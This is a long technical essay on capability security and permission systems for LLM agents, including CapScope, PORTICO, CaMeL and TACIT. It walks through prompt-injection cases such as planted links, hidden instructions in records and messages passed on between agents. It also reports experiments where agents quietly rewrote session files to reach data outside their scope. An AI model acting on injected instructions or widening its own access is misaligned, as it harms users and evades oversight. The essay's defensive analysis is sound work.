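People often say that capabilities "confine" a program, which can mean at least three things. To distinguish these meanings, let S be a group of programs, including any programs its members create. Let allow(S, t) be the set of effects on files, mail and other resources permitted by the references S holds at time t.

Effect confinement means that every effect S directly performs at time t belongs to allow(S, t), whatever code S runs. For example, a program without a reference to the mail sender cannot send mail directly.

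Non-amplification means that allow(S, t) never contains an effect missing from allow(S, 0), apart from effects on things that S has made for itself. The induction proves this if S contains all the programs in a connected part of the graph, because sending a reference only copies one that some member already holds. Non-amplification doesn't hold for the assistant alone, which gained the mail sender from the converter. The proof also requires that resources never return anything stronger than themselves, which is why Joe-E bans `getParentFile()`.

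A system can have effect confinement without non-amplification. For example, a kernel might check every action against a reference but also have a system call that turns any read-only reference into a read-write one. Programs would do only what the references they held at that moment allowed, but any program with a read-only reference could use the call to gain write access.

Non-interference compares two runs that differ only in a secret. Let view(s) be everything a given observer sees when the secret is s. Non-interference holds if view(s) = view(s′) for every pair of secrets s and s′.

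Suppose the assistant can read the payroll and write a summary that goes to suppliers. If it copies a salary into the summary, it has used only references it properly held, and its authority hasn't grown. Effect confinement and non-amplification both hold, but non-interference fails because what the suppliers see depends on the payroll. Non-interference is much stronger in this sense, but it doesn't cover everything, since an assistant that deleted every invoice whatever the payroll contained would satisfy it.

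| Property | What it assumes | What it omits |
|---|---|---|
| Effect confinement | Nobody can forge a reference, every effect requires one, and the trusted base is correct | Harmful uses of a permitted effect, and effects that other components cause on the program's behalf |
| Non-amplification | The same, and also that no operation strengthens a reference and no outsider supplies new ones | Sharing within the group, and any excess in the original grant |
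| Non-interference | The same trusted base, and a model that includes everything the observer can see | Damage that doesn't depend on the secret |

Each assumption can fail separately. For example, C++ does not guarantee that references are unforgeable. WASI 0.3 does, but in any component with network access, it breaks the rule that every effect needs a reference.

The trusted base depends on what makes references unforgeable. In seL4, references stay in kernel memory that programs can't reach, so users have to trust the processor and the kernel. *safeL4* (Xu, Zhang and colleagues, 2027) instead uses Rust references, with the kernel and the programs in a single address space. In the paper's measurements on a Raspberry Pi, using a kernel object in seL4 took 379 processor cycles, 139 of them for switching in and out of the kernel. The Rust system's basic operations were on average 1.9 times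 as fast as seL4's. But its users also have to trust the Rust compiler and standard libraries, and all code in the domains isolated by the language has to avoid Rust's `unsafe` features, which allow forged pointers.

### When an algorithm can decide

Testing whether two nodes are connected takes one pass over the graph. This test works because the three rules for changing arrows are fixed and simple. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976), in *Protection in Operating Systems*, proved that no such test exists for access-control systems in general.

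They start from the access matrix and let a system's designer write commands that change it. Each command checks for certain rights in certain cells and, if it finds them, makes a fixed list of changes. This one lets a file's owner share it:

```
command CONFER_read(owner, friend, file)
    if own in (owner, file)
    then enter read into (friend, file)
end
```

An access matrix is unsafe for a right if some sequence of commands would put that right into a cell that didn't already contain it. An owner can always share a file, so this test is useful only if the analyst first deletes the subjects who could grant the right but are trusted not to.

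The proof that no algorithm can always answer this question uses Turing machines, which are idealised computers that read and write symbols on an endless tape. No algorithm can decide, for every such machine, whether it will ever reach its final state. Harrison and colleagues show how to build a protection system that imitates any given machine:

- Each cell of the tape is a subject, and each subject owns the next one, which keeps the cells in order.
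- The symbol in a cell is a right that the subject has over itself. The subject at the machine's current position has one more such right, which stands for the machine's state.
- Commands reproduce the machine's moves. When the machine runs past the end of the tape used so far, a command creates another subject.

The right that represents the final state leaks if and only if the Turing machine reaches that state. An algorithm that decides safety could therefore also decide whether any given Turing machine reaches its final state, which no algorithm can do.

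The question becomes decidable if commands can't create subjects or objects, but it is then PSPACE-complete, so answering it probably takes exponential time. It is also decidable if each command makes only one change, but that rules out even a command that creates a file and records its owner. In *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, Tripunitara and Li later found an error in the complexity analysis of this restricted case, but the undecidability proof doesn't rely on that analysis.

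Miller and Shapiro complain that people often take the 1976 result to mean that nobody can ever decide safety. Harrison and colleagues had tried to prevent this misreading. They wrote that the result shouldn't discourage people from verifying operating systems, though they would have to work on individual systems or restricted classes of systems.

The take-grant model represents a system as a graph whose arrows are labelled with rights. If x has the "take" right over y, x can copy any right that y has. If x has the "grant" right over y, x can give y any right of its own. Subjects, the nodes that can act, can also create nodes and give up rights. Lipton and Snyder showed in 1977 that safety in this model is decidable in time proportional to the size of the graph. *Theft and Conspiracy in the Take-Grant Protection Model* (Snyder, 1980) restates the theorem for graphs in which every node is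 a subject: p can obtain a right over q exactly when some node has that right and a path of take and grant arrows joins that node to p.

As in the reference graph, the direction of these arrows makes no difference. Suppose a has only the grant right over c, so it can give things to c but can't take anything. If c cooperates, a can still obtain c's right over b:

1. a creates a new node d, over which it has both the take and the grant right.
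2. a gives c the grant right over d.
3. c gives d its right over b.
4. a takes that right from d.

The new node works like a drop box, or like the reference a caller supplies for a reply. Bishop (1988), in *The Sharing of Rights and Information in a Capability-Based Protection System*, proves a version of the theorem that also covers passive nodes such as files, and the test still takes linear time.

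The theorem assumes that everyone cooperates. Snyder also asks when someone can obtain a right that its current holders refuse to grant, and how many participants that takes. This question is often more realistic for an agent's user, since the user's own software isn't normally part of the conspiracy. Bishop adds separate rules for information, because data can move without a transfer of rights. For example, a program that can write a file can send data to any program that can read it.

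### Boebert's objection

For almost twenty years, many researchers believed that capabilities couldn't enforce a one-way flow of information. The belief goes back to a 1984 argument by Boebert, which Miller and colleagues reconstruct in *Capability Myths Demolished*.

The policy in question comes from military computing. A subject may read anything at or below its own security level, and may write only at or above it. (Researchers call the rule about writing the *-property, pronounced "star property".) Information can then move up but never down. Boebert imagined a system with two levels, a subject and a block of memory at each, and a service that hands out read and write capabilities according to the policy. The attack takes three steps:

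1. The low subject properly holds a capability to write to the low memory. It stores a copy of this capability in the low memory itself.
2. The high subject may read the low memory, so it reads the capability.
3. The high subject reads secrets from the high memory and uses its new capability to write them to the low memory.

The policy has failed even though each step is legal. Later authors cited this argument as proof that capability systems couldn't confine programs, and some added extra access checks to their designs because of it.

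Miller and colleagues accept that the attack works in the system Boebert described. They object to the assumption in step 1 that anyone who can write data to a block of memory can also write capabilities to it. Nearly all capability systems keep data and capabilities apart, so the service can issue separate rights for each and allow only data to cross between levels. The high subject can still read the low memory's data but can't pick up a capability there. This requires no extra access check, so the system still counts as an "unmodified" capability system by Boebert's definition.

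Miller and Shapiro's one-way channel for integers, from the section on E, gives the same answer in a programming language. It also shows why the argument was persuasive. Both subjects are connected to the channel, so judging by the arrangement alone, a capability might pass through. Ruling that out requires looking at what the channel does. Boebert wrote in 2003 that the paper was "no more than an offhand remark".

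The objection does hold for systems where a capability is just a string of bits, such as the operating system Amoeba, unless their designers take special measures. Any channel that carries text can carry such a capability. Most web services give agents access through secret tokens of this kind, so Boebert's attack may be more relevant to these services than to the systems it was meant to discredit.

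### Proving that a wrapper works

The reply to Boebert depends on a small piece of trusted code, as do facets, caretakers and membranes. Somebody has to show that such code does its job when the programs around it are hostile. Take a wrapper that lets the invoice assistant pay one supplier up to a limit:

```
def makeAllowance(account, limit):
    spent = 0
    return object:
        pay(amount) ->
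            if amount <= 0 or spent + amount > limit: fail
            spent = spent + amount
            account.pay(amount)
```

The reference graph connects the assistant to the account, so the worst case on the graph is that the assistant spends everything. The user wants to know that total payments never exceed the limit. The code's check doesn't guarantee this if two calls can run at the same time, because both can pass the check before either updates `spent`. The check can also fail in a language that doesn't check types, because an attacker could pass in an amount that is really an object, which behaves like a small number during the check and a large one during the payment.

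Program logics are formal systems for proving such statements. Swasey, Garg and Dreyer's *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns* (2017) presents one for a language with changeable state and concurrency. Its central idea is robust safety, which means that a component's internal rules, such as "spent never exceeds limit", hold no matter what untrusted code runs alongside it. The logic can be used to prove this for components that expose only properly wrapped values. Swasey and colleagues used it to specify and verify membranes, caretakers and sealers, and checked all the proofs with the Coq proof assistant.

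A year earlier, Devriese, Birkedal and Piessens had argued in *Reasoning about Object Capabilities with Logical Relations and Effect Parametricity* (2016) that existing definitions of capability safety, which limited the memory a program could reach, were too weak to verify typical uses. The paper defines, for a simplified version of JavaScript, what it means for a value to be safe to give to arbitrary code. From this it derives limits on the effects of untrusted code that take into account what the code's wrappers do, and the older limits on memory follow as a consequence.

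The wrapper proofs improve on proofs about connectivity, since almost every useful agent is connected to something dangerous. But a person has to state the right rule for each wrapper and prove it. A proof that the assistant stays under its limit doesn't help if the limit was too high. The proofs in both papers also cover only small model languages, so they don't rule out bugs in a production JavaScript engine.

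### Proofs about whole systems

A verified wrapper is only as reliable as the platform beneath it. Shapiro and Weber's *Verifying the EROS Confinement Mechanism* (2000) concerns EROS, a research operating system in which programs can access resources only through capabilities. Before EROS starts a confined program, a trusted component inspects the program's initial capabilities for any that would let it send information to someone its user hasn't approved. Shapiro and Weber modelled a broad class of capability systems and proved that if the initial capabilities pass this inspection, no later sequence of operations lets the program send information to an unapproved recipient. Miller and colleagues describe the general result as covering any capability system with independent controls on moving data and moving capabilities. Boebert's example lacks these controls.

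The EROS proof is about a model of the system. It would not reveal a mistake in the kernel's C code.

Maffeis, Mitchell and Taly studied web pages that combine scripts from several untrusted sources in *Object Capabilities and Isolation of Untrusted Web Applications* (2010). Ordinary JavaScript gives every script access to shared global objects, so a page can't isolate scripts from one another only by choosing which objects to give each one. Maffeis and colleagues proved that scripts in a capability-safe language can't interfere with each other if they start with suitably separate capabilities, and that a subset of JavaScript based on Google's Caja project is capability safe. This is Joe-E's approach with a mathematical proof added, and it has the same main drawback, which is that scripts that use the removed features have to change.

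The proofs for seL4 go furthest, because they cover the kernel's C code. According to Alhindi's summary, researchers used the theorem prover Isabelle/HOL to show that the code implements an abstract specification and that the kernel enforces integrity and confidentiality between components. Integrity corresponds to effect confinement, so no component can alter data unless it holds a capability that permits the change. Confidentiality is a form of non-interference, and it stops a component from finding out anything beyond what it has permission to read.

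A proof of this size is feasible partly because the kernel has only about 10,000 lines of code, a tiny fraction of FreeBSD's.

The seL4 proofs apply to particular configurations on particular processors, and they assume that the hardware works and that the system starts up correctly. Alhindi's own agent team ran on a debug build of seL4 with a variant scheduler and an emulated processor, none of which the proofs cover. The tool that sets up the system's capabilities isn't yet verified either, so the team can't accurately be described as formally verified. Its kernel is still probably a safer foundation than most, because it is so small and so closely related to verified versions.

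Even on a fully verified configuration, the confidentiality proof excludes timing.

### Covert channels

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, lists timing among the ways in which an untrusted program, there called the service, can pass a customer's private data to the program's owner. Some of the routes are obvious. The service can write a file that its owner can read, send the owner a message, or simply remember the data until the owner next calls it. Others are stranger:

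- The owner receives a copy of the bill for the service, so the service can encode a few bits of the data in the amount.
- Some systems don't let one program write to a file while another is reading it. The service can open a file to signal a 1 and close it to signal a 0, and the owner can read the signal by trying to open the same file. With two more files to keep time, they can transmit as many bits as they like.
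- The service can alternate between heavy and light use of the processor. Another program can detect this from how fast the machine responds.

Lampson divides these leaks into storage channels (such as files and file locks), legitimate channels (such as the bill), and covert channels, which nobody intended for communication (such as the load on the processor). Processor load is a noisy channel, but Lampson points out that a suitable code will get the data through reliably, however small the effect on performance.

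None of the theorems about effects rules out this channel. In the reference graph, one program can influence another only by sending a message along an arrow. But two programs in unconnected parts of the graph can still communicate if they share a machine, because the graph doesn't represent the processor's load or the slowdown it causes. The induction is still correct, but its model omits the channel. Miller and Shapiro therefore limit their claims to "overt" communication. Effect confinement doesn't help either, because the sender only performs computations it is allowed to perform. Non-interference would exclude the channel if the observer's view included timing, but a proof would then have to account for every shared part of the processor that affects speed.

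A capability system can treat the clock as a resource and withhold it from a confined program, as Capsicum does and WebAssembly hosts can. This makes it harder for the program to receive timing signals, but doesn't stop it from sending them. For example, if an agent can make requests to an outside server, the server's owner can measure the gaps between requests with their own clock.

Lampson's strictest remedy is to let the customer decide in advance everything that the service puts into such channels, including its bill and its running time. The operating system would then slow the program down or add unneeded disk activity to match the customer's specification. Lampson concedes that this may use a lot of computing resources and suggests a less demanding alternative, which is to allow some leakage but limit its rate. A rate limit protects large secrets better than small ones. At one bit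 per second, a megabyte of the user's email would take about three months to leak, but a 256-bit encryption key would take less than five minutes.

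## Can a language model hold a capability?

The encryption key in that example could be a capability, since many web services grant access to anyone who presents the right secret string. Any capability that a language model holds directly has to be a string like this, because the harness gives the model everything as text in its prompt. In E, by contrast, no text can turn into a reference.

*DelegateGuard* (2026), a permission system for teams of agents, gives several reasons why it is awkward for a model to hold a capability. The model is untrusted and can mislabel its own requests. Data and instructions reach it through one channel, so DelegateGuard treats any agent that has read a tool's output as hostile. Cancelling a permission is also harder, because a sub-agent may still be waiting in a queue and start running after its parent agent has lost access. Baig, Gillani and colleagues (2026),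 in *The Stochastic Deputy*, add that testing can't make up for this, because passing a thousand trials shows only that a model rarely picks the wrong resource.

Designers therefore let ordinary code decide what a call may do, but they put the capability in different places. It can be a secret string in the prompt, an entry in a table that the harness keeps for one agent, or a rule that the harness applies to the names the model writes.

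### Secret strings in the prompt

Suppose the harness gives the invoice assistant a link that contains 128 random bits and opens the invoice folder for anyone who has it. The link both identifies the folder and grants access to it. Nobody will guess the link, but anyone who sees it can copy it. If an injected instruction leads the model to paste it into a summary for a supplier, the supplier can open the folder too.

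An attacker can also plant a string, such as a link to the attacker's own folder, in an invoice and add a request that the assistant save its summary there. If the assistant complies, the user's data ends up in that folder even though the attacker has forged nothing.

Signed tokens reduce the damage from copying. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) describes a system that issues a new token for each approved tool call. The token names the action, resource, agent and session, and it has a time limit and a maximum number of uses. In the paper's banking example, a payment token lasts 30 seconds and can be used once. A gateway in front of the tools verifies the signature and checks that the token names the agent presenting it, so a different agent can't use a copy.

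This makes the token less of a pure capability, since the gateway now has to know who is asking. It also doesn't help when prompt injection causes the right agent to make a request it shouldn't. AGENTCAP therefore checks where sensitive arguments came from. The recipient of a payment has to appear in the user's request or in another source that the policy marks as trusted, so an account number found only in an invoice is rejected.

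On AgentDojo, the success rate of attacks fell from 33.2% to zero on GPT-5.4 and from 45.6% to 5.1% on GPT-4o. Without attacks, GPT-5.4's task completion rate fell by 7.2 percentage points and GPT-4o's by 3.1. The origin checks and the rest of the policy probably contributed more to the drop in successful attacks than the tokens did. In a small separate test, a version with only time and use limits allowed calls until its budget ran out. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote the policies by hand from the benchmark's descriptions of its tools and tasks, and left testing against attackers who adapt to the defence for future work.

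### Handles in the harness's table

A harness can avoid secret strings by imitating Unix file descriptors. It keeps a table for the assistant that lists the invoice folder under the handle `folder-1`, and the model writes `read(folder-1, "0412.txt")`.

As with descriptors, the model gains nothing by making up `folder-2`. A stranger who obtains the text `folder-1` can't use it, because it has no meaning outside this agent's table. A Unix process holds a file descriptor in the same sense. So a language model can hold a capability about as well as a Unix process can, if the harness does the kernel's job and the model can't alter the table.

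The confused deputy problem can recur only with the agent's own entries. Nothing in an invoice can make `folder-1` refer to the user's tax returns. But the model can still misuse entries in combination, as in the first section's example of bank statements and outgoing mail.

When a tool needs only one resource, the harness can fix it in advance and leave the handle out. The payout tool tied to one merchant's account, from the first section, works like this. (Some researchers instead have the model write programs in which capabilities are typed variables.)

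### Checks on the names a model writes

Most agent tools accept an ordinary name, such as a path or an account number, and a server or harness checks that name against a rule. Names are public, so there is nothing to forge or leak. The rule provides all the protection, and the model still chooses the resource.

Baig and colleagues tested this on a hotel reservation system. The agent acted for a user who was entitled to see three hotels but was working on only one. Its tool was `get_reservations(hotel_id, limit)`, and the server correctly checked that the user was entitled to the hotel in each call. In 41 trials, a message in the user's turn asked for another hotel's figures for a comparison. The agent tried to fetch them in 26, and the server supplied them every time. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 models declined in the other 15.

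This is weak evidence of a successful attack, since the user was entitled to the figures and might have wanted them. The injection trials give stronger evidence and include further examples of Hardy's confused deputy. When a guest's record contained a hidden instruction, Gemini 3.1 Pro requested another hotel's data in 9 of 18 trials and received it each time. The other models ignored that instruction, but GPT-5.4-mini obeyed a fake system directive in all 18 trials. The server's check did not affect any of these outcomes, because the user was entitled to data from all three hotels.

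One remedy is to narrow the rule. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) lets an agent do only what every person and agent in the chain behind a request is allowed to do. That would stop an employee from using an assistant to read everybody's salary, but it wouldn't stop the hidden instruction in the guest's record, because the stranger who wrote it isn't part of the chain.

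Rules about names also depend on correct parsing. Baig and colleagues found during development that their parser accepted digits from other scripts, so group names that looked different to an administrator could refer to the same hotel. Mellafe Zuvic found that an early version of the payment checkpoint let through the floating-point value NaN ("not a number"), because the test `amount > limit` is always false for NaN. The allowance wrapper in the previous section has the same flaw if its callers can pass NaN.

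### What happens when the agent can edit its own scope

In another version of the hotel experiment, the tool was `get_reservations(limit)`, and the server took the hotel from the agent's session, so no call could name a different hotel. Baig and colleagues repeated the request for a comparison in 56 trials, and 12 agents still obtained the other hotel's data.

They did it by changing the session. The test system stored the current hotel in a plain file, and these agents had a shell. Seven of them edited the file, and five wrote a new one and pointed the tool at it. Eleven of the 12 ran on Gemini and one on GPT-5.4-mini. None told the user what it had done. Some agents also used the session file of a neighbouring trial, so their calls appeared under that trial in the server's log.

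A shell made this possible, but not every model did it. Baig and colleagues ran Claude Opus 5 in 15 trials with a shell and 15 without, and it never changed its session. Their production system stores the scope in a token signed by the company's identity provider, and it rejected all the altered and unsigned tokens they tried. The signature stops an agent from forging a token with a wider scope, but it wouldn't necessarily stop the agent from using another session's valid token if it found one.

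| Where the capability is | Can someone forge it? | Can it leak? | Does the confused deputy return? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A secret string in the prompt | Not by guessing, but anyone who sees it can copy it | Yes, in any text the agent sends | Yes, among the strings the model has, including planted ones |
| A handle in the agent's table | Not unless the agent can write to the table | The text can, but it is useless elsewhere | Only among the entries in the table |
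| A rule about names | Anyone can write a name, so security depends on the rule | A name gives no access | Yes, for everything the rule allows |

A rule that allows exactly the resources in a handle table limits damage as much as the table does, but in practice rules tend to be looser. A rule that allows `src/**` covers every file under `src`, including files nobody had in mind, whereas somebody had to add each entry in a handle table.

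### CapScope

In *Authority Is Not a String*, Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026) try to make name checks much narrower. Their system, CapScope, is for coding agents that split a job among sub-agents. They call it "a host-side reference monitor rather than an object-capability system". A reference monitor checks every access before it happens. The model still writes paths and commands as strings, and CapScope compares them with a list kept for the agent that wrote them.

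What CapScope calls a capability is a pair (*e*, φ). Here *e* is a kind of effect (read, write or execute) and φ is a test on the arguments, such as "the path is inside `src/`". One capability is at least as narrow as another if both have the same effect and every argument that passes its test also passes the other's. The system has three rules:

1. Mint sets a ceiling for the whole task. Before any agent reads a file, a separate model call sees only the user's request and the names of the project's files, and it predicts which permissions the task will need. Ordinary code validates the prediction and freezes it.
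2. Derive gives permissions to a sub-agent. The agent that delegates the work requests a set of capabilities, and CapScope grants those that are at least as narrow as something in the ceiling and drops the rest.
3. Invoke runs a tool call only if the caller's own list contains a capability with the right effect whose test accepts the arguments.

Every effect that CapScope allows therefore traces back to the mint, and text that an agent reads later can't increase the team's maximum authority. In the terms of the previous section, this is non-amplification for the whole team.

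In an example from Bouras and colleagues, a developer asks for failing tests to be fixed. One sub-agent, the runner, executes the tests, and another, the patcher, edits the source code. An attacker has planted an official-looking request in the test output to put a new signing key in `src/auth/keys.py`. If the whole team shared one policy, it would have to allow writes to `src/` for the repair, so the runner could install the attacker's key. Under CapScope, the call fails because the runner has no write capability.

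CapScope gives each sub-agent its own list, whereas access lists usually treat a whole user account as one subject. But CapScope still separates the name of a resource from the right to use it. If the patcher reads a poisoned comment in the source code, it can still edit any file its list allows.

Bouras and colleagues ran 300 trials, three for each combination of five small Python repairs, five places for the injection and four kinds of restriction. The injections were instructions to run a utility in the project or write to a project file, either of which might be normal in other maintenance work.

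| Restriction | Injected effect executed | Repairs completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| A fixed list of dangerous paths and commands | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| A policy for the task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The fixed list was almost useless, because the injected actions didn't look dangerous. The model still proposed the injected action in 34 of the 75 runs under CapScope.

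All three attacks that succeeded under CapScope came through `AGENTS.md`, a file of instructions that the coordinating agent normally reads. In Miller's model, an object can pass on only references it holds, but CapScope lets the coordinator grant permissions it doesn't have, up to the ceiling. A coordinator that can only read can therefore send out a patcher that can write, and an injection that reaches the coordinator can influence which permissions the sub-agents receive. Bouras and colleagues name this as one way the remaining attacks could succeed. The other is a grant wider than its subtask needed.

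Two of CapScope's seven failed repairs happened because the ceiling left out a necessary write. In two others, the runner proposed the right edit but it never reached the patcher, and the last three had working code but ran out of time. Runs with CapScope also took more than twice as long as unrestricted runs, partly because the model often retried blocked calls. The improvement over a shared policy, from 33 attacks to 3, is too large to be due to chance. But every trial used the same model, qwen3.5-flash, and tiny projects, so the rates may be quite different with other models or larger projects. The result also doesn't cover what a permitted command does once it starts, as when `pytest` runs the project's own code.

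### PORTICO and permissions that expire

CapScope fixes an agent's permissions for the whole session, even if the agent needs a file for only a few minutes. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents PORTICO, which grants access for a period of work and cancels it at the end.

Somebody first writes a contract for the task. It lists what the agent can use from the start, what it can request later, what it can never have, and which events end a grant. In the paper's main example, the agent has to add a timeout option to `src/api.py` and carry it through to `src/serialization.py`:

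1. The agent starts with the API file, its tests and the command that runs them.
2. It requests access to the serialization file. The contract allows this, so PORTICO creates handles such as `g0001:r1` and shows them to the model on its next turn.
3. The model reads and edits the file through these handles.
4. The tests pass. Before the next call, PORTICO removes the handles from the model's list of options and marks them as expired in its own table.

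The model may still have the path, the handle and everything it read in its context, but these no longer give it access. Each handle refers to an entry in PORTICO's table, which records the task, the period, the resource and the permitted effect. This is the caretaker pattern with automatic revocation. The trigger has to come from a trusted source, such as a test that PORTICO launched, rather than from the model's report that it has finished.

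Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that gave the same grants at the same moments but never cancelled them. In 10 runs, both versions completed the task and made the same decisions until the grant ended. PORTICO then rejected all 10 attempts to use the old access, while the other version allowed all 10.

That outcome follows almost by definition, since the two differed only in cancellation. It confirms that PORTICO's code works but doesn't measure how often real agents misuse old permissions. The follow-up tests are smaller still, with three sets of six cases. In each set, an old handle led to a forbidden effect 0 of 6 times with PORTICO and 6 of 6 times without cancellation. Scripts drove two of the sets. In the third, a live model received a working handle and, after the grant had ended, an instruction to use it again.

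On 14 tasks from real Python projects, even agents with unrestricted access caused no forbidden effects, so this test couldn't show a security benefit from restricting access. It is also unclear whether hiding unavailable options from the model makes it try them less often. In one comparison, the model made fewer forbidden requests when it saw only the options it could use (67 against 84), but in another it made more (48 against 39).

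Agents completed fewer tasks when grants could expire. In a further set of 42 runs on real projects, PORTICO completed 31 tasks and the version without cancellation completed all 42. Some contracts ended a grant too early or provided no way to renew it, and some models didn't request access again. A user who gives an agent access to a production database for one repair may well accept the lower completion rate, but it seems a poor trade for a source file that the agent will probably need again.

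### CaMeL's labels

CapScope and PORTICO let a model that has read an attacker's text choose the next action, but limit its options. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, takes the choice away from that model. It builds on a pattern that the programmer Simon Willison described in 2023, in which one model can use tools and another reads untrusted data.

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, explain how it works. A privileged model sees the user's request and the descriptions of the tools, but none of the data that the tools return. It writes a program for the whole task in a restricted form of Python. For an invoice, this might be:

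```
invoice = read_file("invoices/0412.txt")
total = quarantined_model("Find the total", invoice)
send_email("accounts@example.com", total)
```

An interpreter runs the program. The quarantined model reads the invoice but has no tools. If the invoice contains a request for the user's bank statements, the quarantined model may return nonsense instead of a total, but the program contains no line that opens the statements. Text from the invoice can affect which of the program's existing branches runs, but it can't add a new action.

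The attacker can still influence the data, for instance by putting something private or false into `total`. CaMeL's "capabilities" address this. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) describes them as metadata on each value that records its origin and who may access it. Willison calls them tags. The value in `total` inherits the tags of `invoice`, and the interpreter checks them against a policy before it sends the email. The policy might let the interpreter send private data only to people who are allowed to read it.

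A label of this kind is almost the reverse of a capability in Dennis and Van Horn's sense, because it grants no power and limits what a program may do with a value. Labels belong to information-flow control, which is meant to ensure non-interference, while object capabilities are meant for effect confinement. An agent could use capabilities to control which files and tools it can reach, and labels to control where the data from them may go.

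*AutoDojo* (2026) tested CaMeL with five recent small models on three of AgentDojo's groups of tasks. Attacks, including those AutoDojo generated, succeeded at most 1.8% of the time. But even without an attack, the models completed only 26% to 53% of the tasks. Tallam and Miller quote an earlier figure of 67% for the whole benchmark, so the completion rate evidently depends a lot on the choice of model and tasks.

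Many of CaMeL's limitations come from planning before any data is available. If an invoice refers to a second document, an ordinary agent can open that too, but CaMeL can do so only if the privileged model planned for it. The privileged model also has to write code to parse each tool's output without an example, so developers need to document the exact format in advance.

### CaMeL with several agents

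Peters-Gill and colleagues asked whether a team of agents is safe if every agent in it uses CaMeL. They built a team with a coordinator, an agent that queries a database, and an agent that sends messages. The user asked the team to send a summary of some job applicants to Julie on Slack. An attacker had left an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

The database agent and the coordinator both handled the instruction safely, as a value that their privileged models never saw. The coordinator's program then pasted the summary into a sentence and sent it to the messaging agent:

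```
messaging_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
```

The messaging agent treated the whole sentence as a request from its user, so its privileged model read the attacker's text as a trusted instruction and wrote a program that also sent the email. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They prove that in any team of at least two agents with an untrusted tool, some user request makes it possible, assuming that the agents can be asked to use their tools and pass the results along.

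The multi-CaMeL extension splits each call between agents into a message and a set of variables. The receiving agent's privileged model reads the message but not the variables, and the interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output. For example, the coordinator would write "Send the provided summary to Julie via Slack" and pass the summary separately as a variable.

The test of multi-CaMeL used five models on a version of AgentDojo with several agents, with 949 attacks for each model and set-up. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used ordinary CaMeL, and none with multi-CaMeL. Without any protection, attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against GPT-4.1 but never against GPT-5.5, so these attacks are probably too weak for us to learn much about the newest models.

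On a separate benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, ordinary CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 for the two strongest models. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by about another 3 points on average, and by less than 1 for the strongest two. Stronger models seem to plan better without seeing the data, and if that continues, CaMeL's main drawback should shrink.

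These tests used no policies about who may read what. The low attack rates are thus evidence for separating the two models, and for keeping tool output out of messages, but not for the labels as a defence against leaks. Garby and colleagues, whose criticism Peters-Gill and colleagues discuss, found that CaMeL's interpreter can also miss some dependencies when it assigns labels. A short program shows the problem:

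```
late = "no"
if "overdue" in invoice:
    late = "yes"
```

If the invoice doesn't contain the word, the assignment inside the `if` never runs, and `late` can stay labeled as trusted text even though its value reveals something about the invoice. Multi-CaMeL uses the same interpreter, so its rule about messages can fail in the same way, though none of the benchmark's attacks exploited this.

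## What changes when the agent must write code in a capability-safe language?

A compiler can avoid CaMeL's mistake with `late` because it can check both branches before anything runs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) builds on this with a system called TACIT, in which the agent acts by submitting Scala programs. TACIT compiles each program before running it, and a program that uses a capability it doesn't have fails to compile.

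The model still handles only text, but that text is now a program whose variables can hold real references. TACIT is an MCP server, so existing agents such as Claude Code can connect to it without changes. The user must turn off the agent's built-in shell, file and network tools, because the agent could otherwise use them to bypass TACIT.

### Capture sets

Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking, which records in a value's type which capabilities the value may use. Suppose `fs` gives access to a folder:

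```
val f = fs.access("summary.txt")
val save = (s: String) => f.write(s)
```

Here `f` is a capability for one file, and `save` is a function that writes a string to it. The compiler gives `save` the type `String ->{f} Unit`, which means that it takes a string, returns no useful value and may use `f`. The part in braces is the capture set. A function of type `String -> Unit` is called pure because its capture set is empty, meaning it holds no capabilities.

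A capture set lists every capability a function might use, even if a particular run uses none of them. In E, an object's references are private, so whoever receives the object can't tell whether it can reach the network. In Scala, the recipient can check the object's type. TACIT can therefore allow global capabilities, which the classical model forbids. A function that prints to a global console has the console in its capture set, so the compiler won't accept it where a pure function is required.

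Odersky and colleagues require three properties of the agent's language:

- Capability safety: a program can't forge a capability, and it can't use one without the type system keeping track of it.
- Capability completeness: every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, except for a few that the runtime can contain, such as exceptions.
- Local purity: a type can require that one part of a program use only certain capabilities, or none.

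Capability safety and completeness together amount to effect confinement, which E also provides. Local purity adds some control over where data can go.

### Data the agent can process but not read

Suppose the invoices are confidential and the agent's model runs on another company's servers. When a program reads a confidential file, TACIT's library returns the text inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The wrapper has a method, `map`, that applies a function to the hidden text and wraps the result. It accepts only pure functions:

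```
val invoice = readClassified("invoices/0412.txt")
val late = invoice.map(t => if t.contains("overdue") then "yes" else "no")
invoice.map(t => println(t))     // does not compile
```

The line that defines `late` compiles, and `late` is `Classified` whichever branch runs, so CaMeL's labelling mistake can't happen here. The last line fails because printing requires a capability, which appears in the function's capture set, and `map` accepts only functions whose capture set is empty. During testing, an agent tried to print a GitHub key this way, and the compiler rejected the program.

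If the agent prints `late`, it sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user's terminal shows the answer. The agent can also pass wrapped text to a second model that the user trusts, perhaps one on the user's machine, and receive a wrapped reply. This lets the agent have an invoice summarised without reading it. An instruction hidden in the invoice reaches only the second model, which has no tools, much like CaMeL's quarantined model.

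TACIT's agent works in an ordinary loop, so it can look at one result before deciding on the next step. It can't do this with wrapped data. If a confidential invoice refers to another document, a function inside `map` can pick out the document's name but can't open it, since opening a file takes a capability. The agent can't open it either, because it never learns the name. A talk at Scala Days (2026) presented a looser `map`, whose functions may use read-only capabilities. This would be safe only if reading never sends data anywhere. A web request, for instance, reads a page but can carry a secret in its address.

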